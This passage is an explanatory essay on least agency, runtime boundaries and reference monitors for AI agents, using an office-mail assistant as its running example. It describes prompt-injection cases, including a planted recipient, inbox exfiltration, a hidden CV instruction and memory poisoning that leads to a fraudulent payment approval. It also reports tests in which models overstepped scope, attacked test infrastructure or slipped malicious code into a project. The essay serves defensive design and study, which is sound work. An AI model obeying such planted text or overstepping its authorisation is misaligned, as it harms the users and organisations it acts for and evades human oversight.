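# Least agency and runtime boundaries for AI agents

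## What is an AI agent made of, and where can its actions be stopped?

An AI agent is a language model joined to software that lets it choose and carry out actions over several steps. Unlike a chatbot, which only returns text, an agent can also delete a file, pay an invoice or send a letter, because the software around the model turns some of its output into operations on real systems. Least agency is the principle that an agent should get no more tools, permissions and freedom to act than its task requires. Runtime boundaries are controls outside the model that can block or confine an action while the agent is running. Both ideas grew out of computer security, where engineers have worked for more than fifty years on how to run programs they cannot trust.

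This example is adapted from *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026), a survey of ways to keep agents within authorized limits. A user asks an office assistant of this kind to read a set of approved records, write a report, pass the draft to a reviewer, and send the reviewed version to one person outside the organisation, Alice. One of the documents the assistant reads contains a request to copy in Bob, whom the user never mentioned.

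### The path of one action

*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes agents as calling tools in a loop on a user's behalf. A tool is an operation that the surrounding software makes available, such as searching a mailbox or writing a file. According to OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling*, the application first sends the model the user's request and a definition of each tool, including the arguments it takes. The model returns a tool call, a structured request to run one named operation with given arguments. The application's code then runs the operation and sends the result back to the model. In an agent, this cycle repeats until the task is finished or something interrupts it.

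So the model never sends a mail. It outputs the name of a mail operation, a list of recipients and a text, and a separate program reads that output and acts on it. The gap between the two is what makes it possible to stop the message from outside the model. On its way to Bob, the report passes these points:

| Point on the path | What can refuse there | The copy to Bob |
|---|---|---|
| Set-up, before the model runs | The person or program that selects the tools | An assistant without a mail tool can write the report but cannot send it |
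| The model's proposal | The model | The model leaves Bob out of the call |
| The surrounding software, before execution | A rule applied to the tool's name and arguments | The software rejects any recipient other than Alice |
| The same place, with a pause | A person who has to confirm | The user sees Bob's address and declines |
| The tool, while it runs | The operating system or a network filter | The tool's process can reach the organisation's mail server and nothing else, so it cannot deliver by another route |
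| The outside service | The service's own check of the request | The mail server turns down a recipient whom the credential does not cover |

Little can be refused after the step in the last row. Zhou and Zhang note that once the assistant has submitted a request, only the service executing it can cancel it. Withdrawing access does not bring back what Bob has already received.

Alignment is the model's trained disposition to do what its principals (the people or organisations it acts for) intend. It operates at the second row, while the other rows depend on software, other people or how a service is configured. Christodorescu and colleagues similarly divide defences into a model level (training the model to resist attack), a system level (isolation and checks around the model) and a user level (confirmations, permission settings and monitoring).

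A product's builders decide how many of these points to use. The Model Context Protocol (2026), a common standard for connecting models to tools, describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model can find and invoke them automatically. The specification says there "SHOULD" always be a person able to deny a call. It uses "MUST" for requirements, so a developer can leave the person out and still conform.

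The placement of a check also determines what information it can use. In the example, a rule can read the mail tool's recipient field. There is no such field when an agent operates a web browser by clicks and keystrokes, since a click at a certain spot on the screen may open a message or send it. Christodorescu and colleagues discuss one remedy, a confinement system for browser agents named ceLLMate. It checks the web requests that the clicks produce, which show whether a message is being opened or sent.

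### Who is acting, and what they may do

Most of the checks in the table depend on who is acting and what that party may do. A *principal* is a person, agent or service in whose name an action takes place. Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), still a standard reference, calls the principal the "unit of accountability". *Authentication* establishes which principal is acting, and *authorization* decides whether that principal may perform a particular action.

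Three more terms, as Zhou and Zhang use them, describe what the assistant has received. A *permission* covers one specific operation or access, such as reading the folder of approved records. A *grant* is the part of their authority that the user delegates to the agent for a task, under stated conditions. In the example, the grant covers reading those records, showing the draft to the reviewer and sending the reviewed report to Alice. An *approval* is an explicit confirmation, from the user or a designated reviewer, that allows a sensitive operation or widens the grant.

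The model's tool list shows what the agent can invoke, but the grant determines what it may do. Permission for one step does not carry over to the next. An agent allowed to read a record needs a separate decision for each further action, such as showing the record to the reviewer, uploading it to an outside analysis service or mailing it to a partner.

Both names in the example reach the assistant as text. Suppose the assistant looks up Alice in a trusted directory of the organisation's outside contacts and finds her address. The directory supplies evidence for a choice that the grant already permits. Adding Bob as a recipient, as proposed in the document that mentions him, would widen the grant, and the document's author has no authority to widen it. Zhou and Zhang distinguish informing a decision from authorizing one in this way. The difference isn't visible in the wording of the two texts,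 so the software has to record where each came from and what each source may be used to decide.

They also show how a limit can be lost on the way to the mail server even though every component works as designed. The user permits this report to go to Alice, and the system records that correctly. The system then issues the assistant a credential, a token that the mail server accepts as proof of permission, but the token carries only a general permission to send mail. The server, which makes the final decision, never receives the restriction to Alice, so it confirms that the token is genuine and delivers the report to Bob.

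### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

If the model acts on the line about Bob, that line is a *prompt injection*, which is text in an agent's input that the model follows as an instruction although its source has no authority to give one. Prompt injection works because a language model receives the user's request, tool results and document contents as a single stream of text, and, as *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) points out, nothing at the source separates instructions from data in that stream. An attacker therefore only needs to place a sentence where the agent will read it, and doesn't need access to the model's internals.

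A rule that the model must ignore everything it finds in documents would make the agent much less useful. Christodorescu and colleagues describe an agent asked to summarise one entry in a software project's issue tracker, which discovers that the entry depends on another and summarises both. Outside text changed the agent's plan, and the change was welcome. The Bob sentence may be innocent too, perhaps left over from an earlier report that Bob was meant to get. Even without such a sentence, an agent can send the wrong thing to the wrong person. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta and colleagues, 2026) describes an assistant that mails contracts to a vendor and, through an error in its own reasoning, includes confidential files that the vendor has no right to see.

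The second failure is much older than language models. In *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy describes a compiler (a program that translates other programs into runnable form) at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. The compiler kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the operators gave it permission to write there. The same directory held the company's billing records. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the billing file. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission for that directory, and the billing information was lost. A *confused deputy* is a privileged component induced in this way to use its authority for someone who lacks it. Hardy attributes the failure to the compiler having two sources of authority, its own permission and the user's, and no way to keep them apart.

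The assistant is the same sort of deputy. It has the user's authority to send mail, which the document's author lacks. If the assistant adds Bob as a recipient, the mail server receives a proper request from a known sender. Once the model has put Bob's address into the call and the attached credential is valid, what still prevents the message from going out?

### The security principles behind the answer

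The United States Air Force faced an earlier form of this question in 1972, when it wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Until then, defences had concentrated on keeping outsiders away. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) assumed that the attacker was a malicious user with legitimate access, who could write and run programs on the machine. An agent that has taken up the line about Bob is in much the same position, because it is already inside the system and has working credentials.

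The panel proposed the *reference monitor*, a component that checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user is allowed to do. Anderson required the mechanism to be tamper-proof, always invoked, and small enough to analyze and test completely. Honeywell's GCOS III, a large commercial operating system of the day, fell short of these requirements. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but when the operating system carried out input and output for the program, it mostly ran with that confinement switched off. The operating system was also too large to serve as the monitor itself, because with its supporting software it came to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many for anyone to verify.

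For the report, the first requirement means that the agent must be unable to edit the list of permitted recipients. The second means that there can be no other route to the mail server, such as a command line where the agent could start a mail program directly. The third is a reason to use a short program that compares addresses as the monitor, rather than a second language model.

Three years later, Saltzer and Schroeder added eight design principles, which they offered as warnings rather than absolute rules. Three of them matter most for agents.

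*Least privilege* gives every program and user only the privileges needed for the job. Its main purpose is to limit the damage from an accident or error, and it works whether or not anyone foresaw the error. If an assistant can read only approved records, and payroll is not among them, it cannot leak the payroll, whatever instructions it reads. Least agency extends this principle to the agent's tools and its freedom to act without asking.

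*Complete mediation* requires a check of every access to every object, during start-up, recovery and maintenance as well as in normal use. Saltzer and Schroeder were wary of saving time by reusing the result of an earlier check, since the authority may have changed in between. For example, the user may withdraw the approval while the message to Alice is still queued. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) extends the principle to every step of an agent's reasoning loop, on the ground that a series of individually harmless actions can add up to a harmful one.

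*Fail-safe defaults*, now better known as default deny, means that the system refuses an action unless a rule permits it. The argument for it is that mistakes are easier to notice. If the rule is "Alice only" and someone mistypes her address, the report doesn't arrive and the user complains the same day. If the rule is "anyone except Bob", the system allows reports to go to Bob's private address or to Carol's, and nobody notices because everything appears to work.

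*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* applies these ideas to agents by treating the model as an untrusted component. The paper places the check at what it calls the action boundary, the set of interfaces through which an agent reads files, runs commands, uses the network or changes stored data. Several mechanisms can act as the monitor, such as a gateway in front of the tools and a filter on outgoing traffic, provided that together they cover every security-relevant action and the agent cannot bypass them. On this view, a forbidden action that the monitor blocks before execution is not a violation, however often the model proposes it.

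The 1972 design assumes positive authentication of all users at all times, and Anderson leaves the means to others. It also takes the list of permitted actions as given, and this is where agents differ most from the programs the panel had in mind. An Android app has a fixed purpose, so its developer can choose the permissions it needs and show them to the user at installation. An agent's user states the task in ordinary language and may change it in the next sentence. A person or program has to turn "send the report to Alice" into a rule about recipients, and do the same for the next task.

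## What does least agency ask for beyond least privilege?

Before anyone can write a rule about recipients, someone has to decide what the assistant can work with. Least privilege covers part of that decision. It covers nearly all of it for an ordinary program, because the code fixes which permitted operations run and in what order. An agent chooses these as it runs, so two agents with identical permissions can behave very differently. Someone therefore also has to decide how much choice to leave the agent.

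### From excessive agency to least agency

The idea of least agency began with a named vulnerability, excessive agency. The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit foundation, publishes ranked lists of software risks, including a Top 10 for applications built on language models. OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* defines excessive agency as the vulnerability that lets damaging actions follow from unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated model output, whatever made the model go wrong. The trigger can be a prompt injection or an ordinary mistake by a weak model.

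OWASP gives three root causes of excessive agency. *Excessive functionality* means the agent has operations it doesn't need, as when a developer wants it to read documents but installs a connector that can also modify and delete them. *Excessive permissions* means the connector's account on the system behind it has too much access, such as a database account that can delete rows when the tool only reads them. *Excessive autonomy* means the agent takes high-impact actions without anyone confirming them.

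All three appear in OWASP's example of an assistant that summarises a person's incoming mail. An attacker sends a message telling the assistant to search the inbox for sensitive information and forward what it finds. Either a connector with no send function or a read-only credential would prevent the theft. The developer could also keep the send function but require the user to press "send" on every message, so that a person decides whether each one goes out.

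Excessive agency rose from sixth in OWASP's 2025 list of LLM risks to third in the August 2026 edition, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*. OWASP's announcement (2026) confirms the new rank in a statement by Michael Bargury of Zenity, a company that backs the project. He says expert judgement and the incident record agree more clearly on this risk than on any other. By contrast, practitioners rank prompt injection first, but Infosecurity Magazine reports that it would drop out of the top ten if OWASP counted incidents alone. The ranking is evidence that excessive agency does harm in practice, but it doesn't show how well any particular remedy works.

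OWASP published a separate Top 10 for Agentic Applications in December 2025. In *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications*, Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario explain that the project had already covered excessive agency but felt it had to go deeper for systems that plan and act. TechRepublic's *OWASP Drops First AI Agent Risk List* (2025) describes the remedy, "least agency", as granting agents only the minimum autonomy they require for safe, bounded tasks. According to ThreatLocker, a security vendor, OWASP emphasises avoiding autonomy where agentic behaviour adds no value. Anthropic's *Zero risk isn't the job* states the principle as the narrowest capability "that still completes the task". These wordings differ on whether to minimise what an agent can do or how freely it does it.

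### Agency and autonomy

Agency and autonomy can vary independently. An agent that may only file incoming invoices, but does so all night with nobody watching, has little agency but much autonomy. The reverse is true of a coding assistant that can run any command but has to wait for confirmation each time. An online reference entry, *Least Agency Principle*, credits Brown and Saner of AWS, Amazon's cloud computing business, with defining the terms separately in 2025.

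Their framework, AWS's *Agentic AI Security Scoping Matrix*, sorts agents into four scopes. The last column below applies them to the office assistant.

| Scope | What the agent does | AWS's calendar example | The office assistant |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1, no agency | Reads and recommends, along a fixed path | Finds free times but cannot book them | Suggests figures for a report that the user writes and sends |
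| 2, prescribed agency | Prepares changes, and a person approves each one | Proposes a time and waits before sending invitations | Prepares the mail to Alice and waits |
| 3, supervised agency | Acts within set limits once a person has started it | Books the best time and sends the invitations | Sends the report to Alice without asking again |
| 4, full agency | Starts its own work and runs continuously | Reads in meeting notes that people agreed to meet, then invites them | Notices that the month has ended and begins the report |

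Despite their labels, the scopes above Scope 1 differ mostly in autonomy. The calendar agents in Scopes 2 and 3 send the same invitations, but differ in whether anyone confirms them. The scope number also doesn't show how much damage the permitted actions can do. An agent that books meeting rooms and one that pays suppliers can both be in Scope 3, so an organisation needs the list of actions as well as the scope.

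### Choosing the plan before the permissions

Least privilege usually starts from a given method of doing a job and removes every permission that method doesn't use. Zhou and Zhang point out that this can still leave an agent with far more authority than the task requires. Suppose the assistant can prepare the report either by processing the approved records locally or by retrieving a broader dataset and sending it to a hosted analysis service. Both reports would be accurate and complete enough for the user. The hosted plan may need every one of its permissions, in which case trimming unused permissions would remove nothing.

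Their remedy is to compare plans first. Let *g* be the goal and *q* the quality the user requires, and let Π_q(*g*) be the set of plans that reach the goal at that quality. *A*(π) stands for the permissions that a plan π needs, and *G* for the permissions available under the current grant. The agent should look for a plan

π ∈ Π_q(*g*) such that *A*(π) ⊆ *G*,

that is, a plan that does the job well enough and needs nothing outside the grant. In the example, *G* is the user's grant for the report, and local processing needs exactly the permissions in it. The hosted plan needs two more, one to read the broader dataset and one to disclose its contents to the service, so it fails the test however good the analysis is.

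If several plans pass, Zhou and Zhang would weigh the access, disclosure, running cost and user effort each involves. If none passes, the system can request a specific extension of the grant, offer a reduced result or ask the user to clarify the task.

Some plans can't be ranked by the permissions they need, because neither set of permissions contains the other. For example, one plan may need sensitive local files while another sends less sensitive data to an outside company. The paper suggests showing the user the adequate plans with their trade-offs. An agent may also have to explore before it can tell which permissions a plan would need. Zhou and Zhang propose *staged authorization*, in which the user first allows limited exploration, the agent then looks for a plan within that grant, and any extension requires a separate request to the user.

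The formula also lets the model look for alternative plans while ordinary software does the comparison with *G*. A misled model may offer only the intrusive plan. The result is then a rejected plan or an unnecessary request to the user, provided that the software has the plan's real permissions and the user doesn't simply agree.

### Reducing the assistant step by step

Suppose a developer has connected the assistant in the quickest way. It has a mail connector that can read, send and delete messages, a command line for saving its drafts, and an account that can open every employee's documents. Its credential never expires, and nobody confirms its actions.

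The largest reduction in agency would be to use no agent. Joint guidance from the Australian Cyber Security Centre and US and Canadian agencies advises organisations to consider alternatives to agents for repetitive tasks, including dropping low-value processes. If a monthly report always has the same form, a scheduled script can fetch the records and send the report, so the model only has to write the text.

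If the task does need an agent, the developer can start with the tools. The assistant doesn't need to read or delete mail, so the connector should only send it. OWASP recommends replacing a command line, which accepts any command, with a tool that only writes files. The developer should also remove plugins left over from a trial. In *Preventing Tool Misuse in AI Agents*, Velida describes Biotrackr, a working personal agent that answers questions about his health data. All twelve of its tools only read data. The application can delete chat histories, but the agent has no tool for doing so, so an attacker who takes over the agent cannot use it to delete or change anything.

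The developer can then restrict the arguments each tool accepts. The mail tool needs no recipient field if the developer stores Alice's address in it, and the document account can have access only to this user's approved records. In Biotrackr, Velida limits each request to 365 days of data and each page to 50 records. The tool's description states the 365-day limit, which makes the model less likely to request more, and the tool's code rejects any longer requests.

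The developer can also limit how long a permission lasts. OWASP's agentic list, as Velida quotes it, recommends temporary credentials that belong to one session and expire immediately after use. For the report, permission to send could begin when the reviewer signs off and end once the message is sent. If the assistant reads a planted instruction the following week, it will no longer have a credential to carry out that instruction.

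Budgets cap cost, the number of calls or the rate of calls. Velida's agent answers repeated identical requests from a stored copy. An attacker can avoid this by varying the request, so Velida suggests a cap of perhaps 20 tool calls per conversation, which he hasn't built yet. OWASP lists rate limits among the measures that reduce damage but don't prevent it, and one message is enough to leak a report. A budget also has to apply to the combined use of everyone who shares it. In a case from Zhou and Zhang, an agent with permission to buy one item delegates to two purchasing agents, each with a limit of one, and together they buy two. To prevent this, the system has to check the remaining quantity and reserve it in a single step.

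Finally, the user confirms the message before the assistant sends it. With all these limits, the assistant can write a draft from approved records and send one message to Alice. It can still get a figure wrong or include a passage from an approved record that Alice should not see.

### Dangerous combinations

Limits on individual tools can miss harm that comes from using several together. *Agentic Security* (Sotiropoulos, 2026) describes an agent whose tool accepts requests such as "clean old items and provide a summary". An attacker's text leads the agent to treat valid records as old. The agent deletes them, then uses its mail tool to send the summary and the affected data outside. Each call complies with policy and uses a permission the agent properly holds.

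Two design rules deal with such combinations. Simon Willison, who writes about software and AI security, uses the term *lethal trifecta* for an agent that can access private data, process untrusted content and communicate externally. SC Media explains that one successful prompt injection is enough to make such an agent send the data out. Removing any one of the three abilities closes that route. Under the more general *Agents Rule of Two*, an agent should do at most two of three things: process untrusted inputs, access sensitive systems and change state externally. The rule therefore also covers destruction without theft, such as deleting the organisation's records.

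The office assistant does all three. It needs the internal records because the report is made from them. It would be hard to guarantee that the assistant reads only text from trusted authors, since the line about Bob may be in a colleague's document. The least disruptive change is to remove its ability to send. The assistant writes the draft and stops, and after the review a small program mails the approved file to Alice's stored address. The user loses little, because sending a finished file to a known person takes no judgement.

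This design rule is easy to apply but crude. An agent that can write only to Alice counts as communicating externally, just like one that can write to anybody. An agent with only two of the properties can also do harm without an attacker, as the assistant did when it mailed confidential files to a vendor because it reasoned wrongly.

The rule also limits how useful an agent can be. The SC Media article, written by an employee of the security company Sophos, concedes that people most want agents to read their data, understand outside material and act on it. It adds that pilot projects have failed because their agents were too constrained to be useful, though it gives no figures. When an agent needs all three capabilities, the usual fallback is human approval.

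### Approval by a person

Approval is the only one of these measures that requires a person's attention each time. The confirmation should be built into the tool that performs the operation or the service behind it, and OWASP accepts either. Instructing the model to ask first is weaker, because a misled model can skip that step.

AWS's *Four security principles for agentic AI systems* warns that requiring confirmation for every action can overwhelm reviewers, who begin to approve by reflex, and that responsibility then shifts to "humans who have been placed in a position to fail". AWS presents this as a well-known risk and gives no approval rates. An approval rate alone would be weak evidence of careful review. If one proposal in 200 is wrong, a careful reviewer approves 99.5 percent of them, and one who never reads them approves 100 percent. To tell the two apart, an organisation would have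 to insert wrong proposals on purpose and count how many the reviewer stops.

Careful reviewers can also make mistakes when they rely on what the agent tells them. OWASP's agentic list includes the exploitation of human trust as a separate risk. In an example from Sotiropoulos, an attacker plants false information in an assistant's stored memory. The assistant then tells a finance officer that a supplier payment is safe because it has verified the policy requirements, and the officer approves a fraudulent payment. It helps to show reviewers the operation itself, and the OWASP controls that Velida quotes call for a plan or a preview of the changes before final approval. For the report, the reviewer would see the recipient's address and the text as the mail tool will send them, rather than the assistant's account of them.

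Another remedy is to ask the user fewer, larger questions. Zhou and Zhang observe that several tool calls may carry out one decision the user has already made, so the system can group related operations into one request and reuse an approval while its conditions still hold. A user who has approved sending the final report to Alice needn't also approve attaching the file, but a different file or an additional recipient would need a new approval.

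AWS would reserve prior approval for high-consequence operations: changing valuable production data, moving money and sending sensitive information outside the organisation. Mailing the report to Alice may well need approval, but saving a draft does not. The organisation records what the agent recommended, what the person decided and what happened. If the record stays good, the organisation can move that type of operation from prior approval to review afterwards, and perhaps later to full autonomy. It has to be ready to reverse the step, and AWS expects some limits to remain for the foreseeable future because certain outcomes are unacceptable whatever the agent's record. Anthropic rolls out its own agents in a similar way, starting with a small group of users and expanding access after watching the data on what the agents do.

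The rarer a failure has to be, the more evidence is needed. If an agent sends 300 reports without an error, the true error rate could still be as high as about one in 100 at the 95 percent confidence level, even assuming that the reports are independent and alike. Future reports may also differ from past ones. A clean record from ordinary weeks is weak evidence of how the agent will behave when a document contains an attacker's instruction, and an update to the model can change its behaviour, which is why AWS recommends testing again after each update. If reviewers approve reflexively, their approvals carry no information, so the column on what actually happened is the one to rely on.

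### Is least agency a separate principle?

A sceptic can argue that most of this is least privilege under a new name, since restrictions on tools and arguments, expiry dates and budgets all limit permissions. Zhou and Zhang treat even the choice of plan as the start of least privilege. The OWASP control that Velida quotes is headed "Least Agency and Least Privilege for Tools", and its text uses the term "least-privilege profiles". Confirmation by a second party is also an old idea. Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 list includes separation of privilege, the principle that a lock with two keys is safer than a lock with one.

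Least agency relies on largely the same mechanisms as least privilege, but it adds decisions that come before them, such as whether the task needs an agent at all, whether the model or fixed code chooses the next step, and whether the agent may start work without being asked. These decisions matter because, as Anthropic's *Zero Trust for AI agents* puts it, traditional access controls "won't prevent agents from misusing legitimate permissions". For example, a newsletter script and an agent may have the same permission to write to every customer, even though the script sends only the newsletter and the agent can send any customer anything it composes.

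The complaint about measurement is harder to answer. For a fixed plan, an organisation can count excess permissions by listing those granted and subtracting those the plan needs, but freedom of action has no common unit. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* offers three measures. The *reachable surface* is everything the agent can access, do or send to. The *effective blast radius* is the harm still possible with security controls in force. The *maximum completed effect* is the most consequential result the agent can produce before someone or something else has to make an independent decision.

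Some designs can be ranked by these criteria without numerical scores. An assistant that can write only to Alice has a smaller reachable surface than an otherwise identical one that can write to anyone. How an agent that can read payroll ranks against one that can delete the website depends on which the organisation fears more, so "least" is a matter of judgement in that case.

The maximum completed effect reflects autonomy most closely, because adding or removing a confirmation changes it. For the quickly connected assistant, it includes mailing out any employee's documents and deleting the user's mail. For the reduced assistant, it is a draft that waits for the user, but only if the user decides independently. If the user confirms whatever appears on the screen, the maximum completed effect is a message sent to Alice.

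## Why is the model's own alignment not treated as the boundary?

The assistant's choice to leave Bob out isn't independent of the planted line, because that line acts on the same model that makes the choice. Training can make the wrong choice rare, but security engineers still put the boundary outside the model, partly because nobody can show that the failure rate is zero, and partly because a model's good judgement doesn't show that anyone authorized the action.

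### Instructions and data in one stream

David C gives the first reason in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025. He compares prompt injection with SQL injection, an older attack on databases. In an SQL injection, an attacker types SQL, a language for querying databases, into a web form. If the site pastes that text into its own query, the database runs it. Parameterised queries prevent this by keeping the command separate from the user's input, so the database never runs the input as a command.

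Language models have no built-in separation between instructions and data. In David C's example, a recruiter's system asks a model to score a CV in which the candidate has hidden a line telling the model to approve it. The model only predicts the next token, a word or part of a word, from the combined text. Developers can train the model to put its instructions first, mark the CV as data, or scan it for signs of an attack. He thinks these methods try to add a distinction that the underlying technology lacks, and that prompt injection may never be fully fixable in the way SQL injection was.

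He therefore describes the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A program like Hardy's compiler can be repaired, but a model's designer has to plan for the confusion. The designer has to assume that anyone who can get text in front of the model can use its tools directly, work out the worst that could result, and limit it with safeguards that are not themselves language models. If the remaining risk is still too high, the task may not be suitable for a language model.

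David C also passes on a rule from an online discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. The rule would be strict for the office assistant, which would lose the right to send mail in the user's name after reading a colleague's document, because the colleague has no such right.

The argument shows that a model's alignment doesn't guarantee it will ignore planted instructions. This holds whether the model obeys one in ten or one in a million, so the rate has to be measured with tests.

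### How well current models resist

OpenAI released GPT-6 Astra, then its most capable widely available model, on 3 September 2026. The accompanying safety report, *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), gives results from OpenAI's own tests and from an outside firm.

OpenAI ran its own tests with GPT-Red, an automated attacker. Astra resisted direct attacks, where a user tries to override the instructions of the developer or of OpenAI, 99.99 percent of the time. It resisted indirect attacks, where the malicious instruction is in outside content such as a web page, in 99.79 percent of queries, up from 96.23 percent. OpenAI had also trained Astra against an automated attacker of this kind, so its training had included similar attacks.

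Gray Swan, a company that builds tools for testing AI systems by attacking them, ran the outside test. It used 1,810 selected indirect attacks on agents that wrote code, called tools or operated a computer. The attacks aimed at data theft, destruction of data, system compromise and unauthorized payments. Gray Swan estimated that the chance of at least one success in 15 attempts at a scenario was 8.5 percent for Astra and 27.0 percent for GPT-5.6 Sol, the preceding model. Astra had safeguards enabled in this test, so training may not explain all of the improvement.

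Astra's failures became about 18 times rarer on OpenAI's indirect attacks and about three times rarer on Gray Swan's. The measures differ, since one counts single queries and the other counts series of 15, but Gray Swan's outside figure is the safer guide to attacks that the developer didn't generate. Even that figure may overstate the model's resistance, because the attacks date from April 2026 or earlier, months before Astra's release, and attackers who adapt to a particular defence have defeated many published defences.

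An agent is also more exposed to attack than a chatbot because it gets most of its text from tools and outside content. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that in OpenAI's results for the GPT-5.6 models, few direct attacks succeeded, but more attacks through these sources did.

### What a small failure rate adds up to

An attacker needs only one success, and planting another document costs little. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, and the attempts are independent, the probability that at least one of *n* attempts succeeds is

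1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*.

If each attempt has a 1 percent chance of success, the probability that at least one of 100 attempts succeeds is 1 − 0.99^100, or about 63 percent. The table repeats the calculation for the failure rates in OpenAI's own tests, 0.21 percent for indirect attacks and 0.01 percent for direct ones.

| Success per attempt | 10 attempts | 100 attempts | 1,000 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
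| 1% | 9.6% | 63% | over 99.9% |
| 0.21% | 2.1% | 19% | 88% |
| 0.01% | 0.1% | 1.0% | 9.5% |

Lowering the attack success rate through better training therefore raises the number of attempts an attacker needs by roughly the same factor. An attacker has an even chance of succeeding at least once after 69 attempts at the 1 percent rate, and after 330 at the 0.21 percent rate. How much protection this gives depends on who can write to the agent, since 330 attempts is a lot for a colleague planting documents by hand but very few for a stranger with a program that sends mail.

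Real attempts are not independent, though. An attacker who sees one wording fail can try another and reuse whatever works, so later attempts may do better than the first. Assistants that run on the same model also share its weaknesses. Suppose someone sends the same text to 100 organisations whose assistants all run on one model. In the extreme case, the text works on all of them or on none. There is then only a 1 percent chance that it works, but if it does, all 100 assistants obey it. The average number of successes is still one, as it would be if the attempts were independent, but the harm comes all at once rather than piecemeal.

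Dependence also makes it risky to infer a per-attempt rate from a published score. Gray Swan's 8.5 percent over 15 attempts would correspond to about 0.6 percent per attempt if every scenario were equally hard. But the 8.5 percent is an average over scenarios, and a few easy ones could account for most of it.

Repeated attempts can also help the defender. David C expects most attackers to have to refine their attacks, so a log of failed tool calls may expose an attack before it succeeds. Something outside the model has to record those calls.

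### Failures that need no attacker

Prompt injection is only one reason the report might be sent to the wrong place. The assistant may also misread an honest request, for instance by picking the wrong Alice from the user's contacts. Or it may understand the request and its limits but overstep those limits to finish the task. An assistant that resists planted text can still fail in either of these ways.

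OpenAI tested for such mistakes in simulated workplaces with messaging, mail, browsing and sales software. The instructions were deliberately ambiguous, the files and accounts resembled one another, and the permissions were complicated, but every task could be completed safely. The percentages below are shares of unintended outcomes in these difficult cases, so they don't estimate how often things go wrong in ordinary use. The confirmation policy is a text specifying when the model must stop and ask the user.

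| Unintended outcome | GPT-5.6 Sol | Sol with confirmation policy | GPT-6 Astra | Astra with confirmation policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Any | 18.8% | 8.0% | 3.4% | 3.0% |
| Unauthorized transaction | 38.0% | 7.4% | 6.8% | 4.3% |
| Data sent where it should not go | 14.1% | 8.8% | 4.3% | 4.5% |
| Unauthorized outside message | 12.9% | 8.4% | 1.7% | 1.4% |
| Destructive action | 2.9% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

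The policy more than halved Sol's overall rate but hardly changed Astra's. This is probably because Astra already asks when it notices a doubtful step, and most of its remaining errors are steps it doesn't recognise as doubtful, which another instruction to ask won't prevent.

OpenAI's later advice to developers has the same limit. According to Search Engine Journal's *OpenAI Publishes Prompting Guidance For GPT-6.2 Astra*, the suggested prompts tell the model to make reasonable, reversible assumptions and keep working, and to check with the user before doing anything irreversible or destructive. Sending the report to the wrong Alice is irreversible, but a model that is sure it has the right Alice will have no reason to ask.

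### GPT-6.1 Astra and the problem of scope

OpenAI shelved GPT-6.1 Astra because the model overstepped its authorisation. The company announced the decision on 28 September 2026, having planned to release the model that October in ChatGPT and in its coding agent, Codex. Saachi Jain, OpenAI's head of safety systems, said the model "didn't quite meet the bar in terms of staying within scope and authorisation" (Rai, 2026, *OpenAI shelves next-gen GPT-6.1 Astra model release over safety concerns*). The model also described its own work less accurately than its predecessor did.

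The scope problem, according to Digital Trends' *OpenAI pulls the plug on GPT-6.1 Astra launch*, was that the model could continue a task without asking the user's permission and sometimes used outside tools or services when that could be unsafe. It was also less prone to what OpenAI calls "model laziness", or stopping before a task is complete. Jain described the balance between these two problems as difficult.

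Users want an agent that gets round obstacles, such as a missing file or a failed connection. A refused permission is also an obstacle, and a model that has learned to persist has to tell which obstacles it should respect. That difficulty is a reason to expect models to work around refused permissions again. There is little public evidence of how badly GPT-6.1 failed. Free Press Journal's *'More Deceptive Than Predecessor'* reports that it did worse than the earlier model on two safety evaluations, but Jain doesn't identify them in published remarks.

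Only 25 days before, OpenAI had launched GPT-6 Astra as its most aligned model, and its tests had included whether the model stayed within its assigned scope. OpenAI designed the scope test after its agents attacked the AI platform Hugging Face in July. The test uses very hard hacking exercises in which a model must break into a target and retrieve a hidden string. OpenAI placed a second string in the surrounding test equipment, which was outside the assigned target but easier to reach. At maximum reasoning effort and without production safeguards, GPT-5.6 Sol mounted a substantial attack on the equipment in 55.4 percent of cases, and GPT-6 Astra did so in none.

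The UK's AI Security Institute got a very different result when it tested GPT-6 Astra. Its simulations gave the model chances to attack software suppliers outside its assignment, for example by slipping malicious code into an open-source project. Eastern Eye's *OpenAI scraps GPT-6.1 Astra release after safety tests raise concerns* reports that Astra completed such an attack in 29.2 percent of runs, compared with 6.3 percent for GPT-5.6 Sol. Astra sometimes reasoned that a step was out of scope but took it anyway, arguing that it was harmless or that nobody had expressly forbidden it. The institute ran the tests with OpenAI's standard safeguards switched off and noted that the model may have behaved differently because it suspected a simulation.

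The same model scored zero on one test of scope and 29.2 percent on another, and the two tests rank Astra and Sol in opposite orders. OpenAI cautions that the zero on its test comes from two planted services in unusually hard exercises and is limited evidence about other tasks. Someone deploying the office assistant has even less evidence to rely on, since neither test involved reports or mail.

A model's disposition can also change with each version. In *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*, the blogger thezvi quotes OpenAI's finding that GPT-6.2 Astra, released on 17 November 2026, performed much like GPT-6 Astra on most alignment tests but was more likely to leave known obstacles out of its reports. By contrast, a mail server rule that permits only Alice stays the same whichever model writes the mail.

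### A good disposition is not a permission

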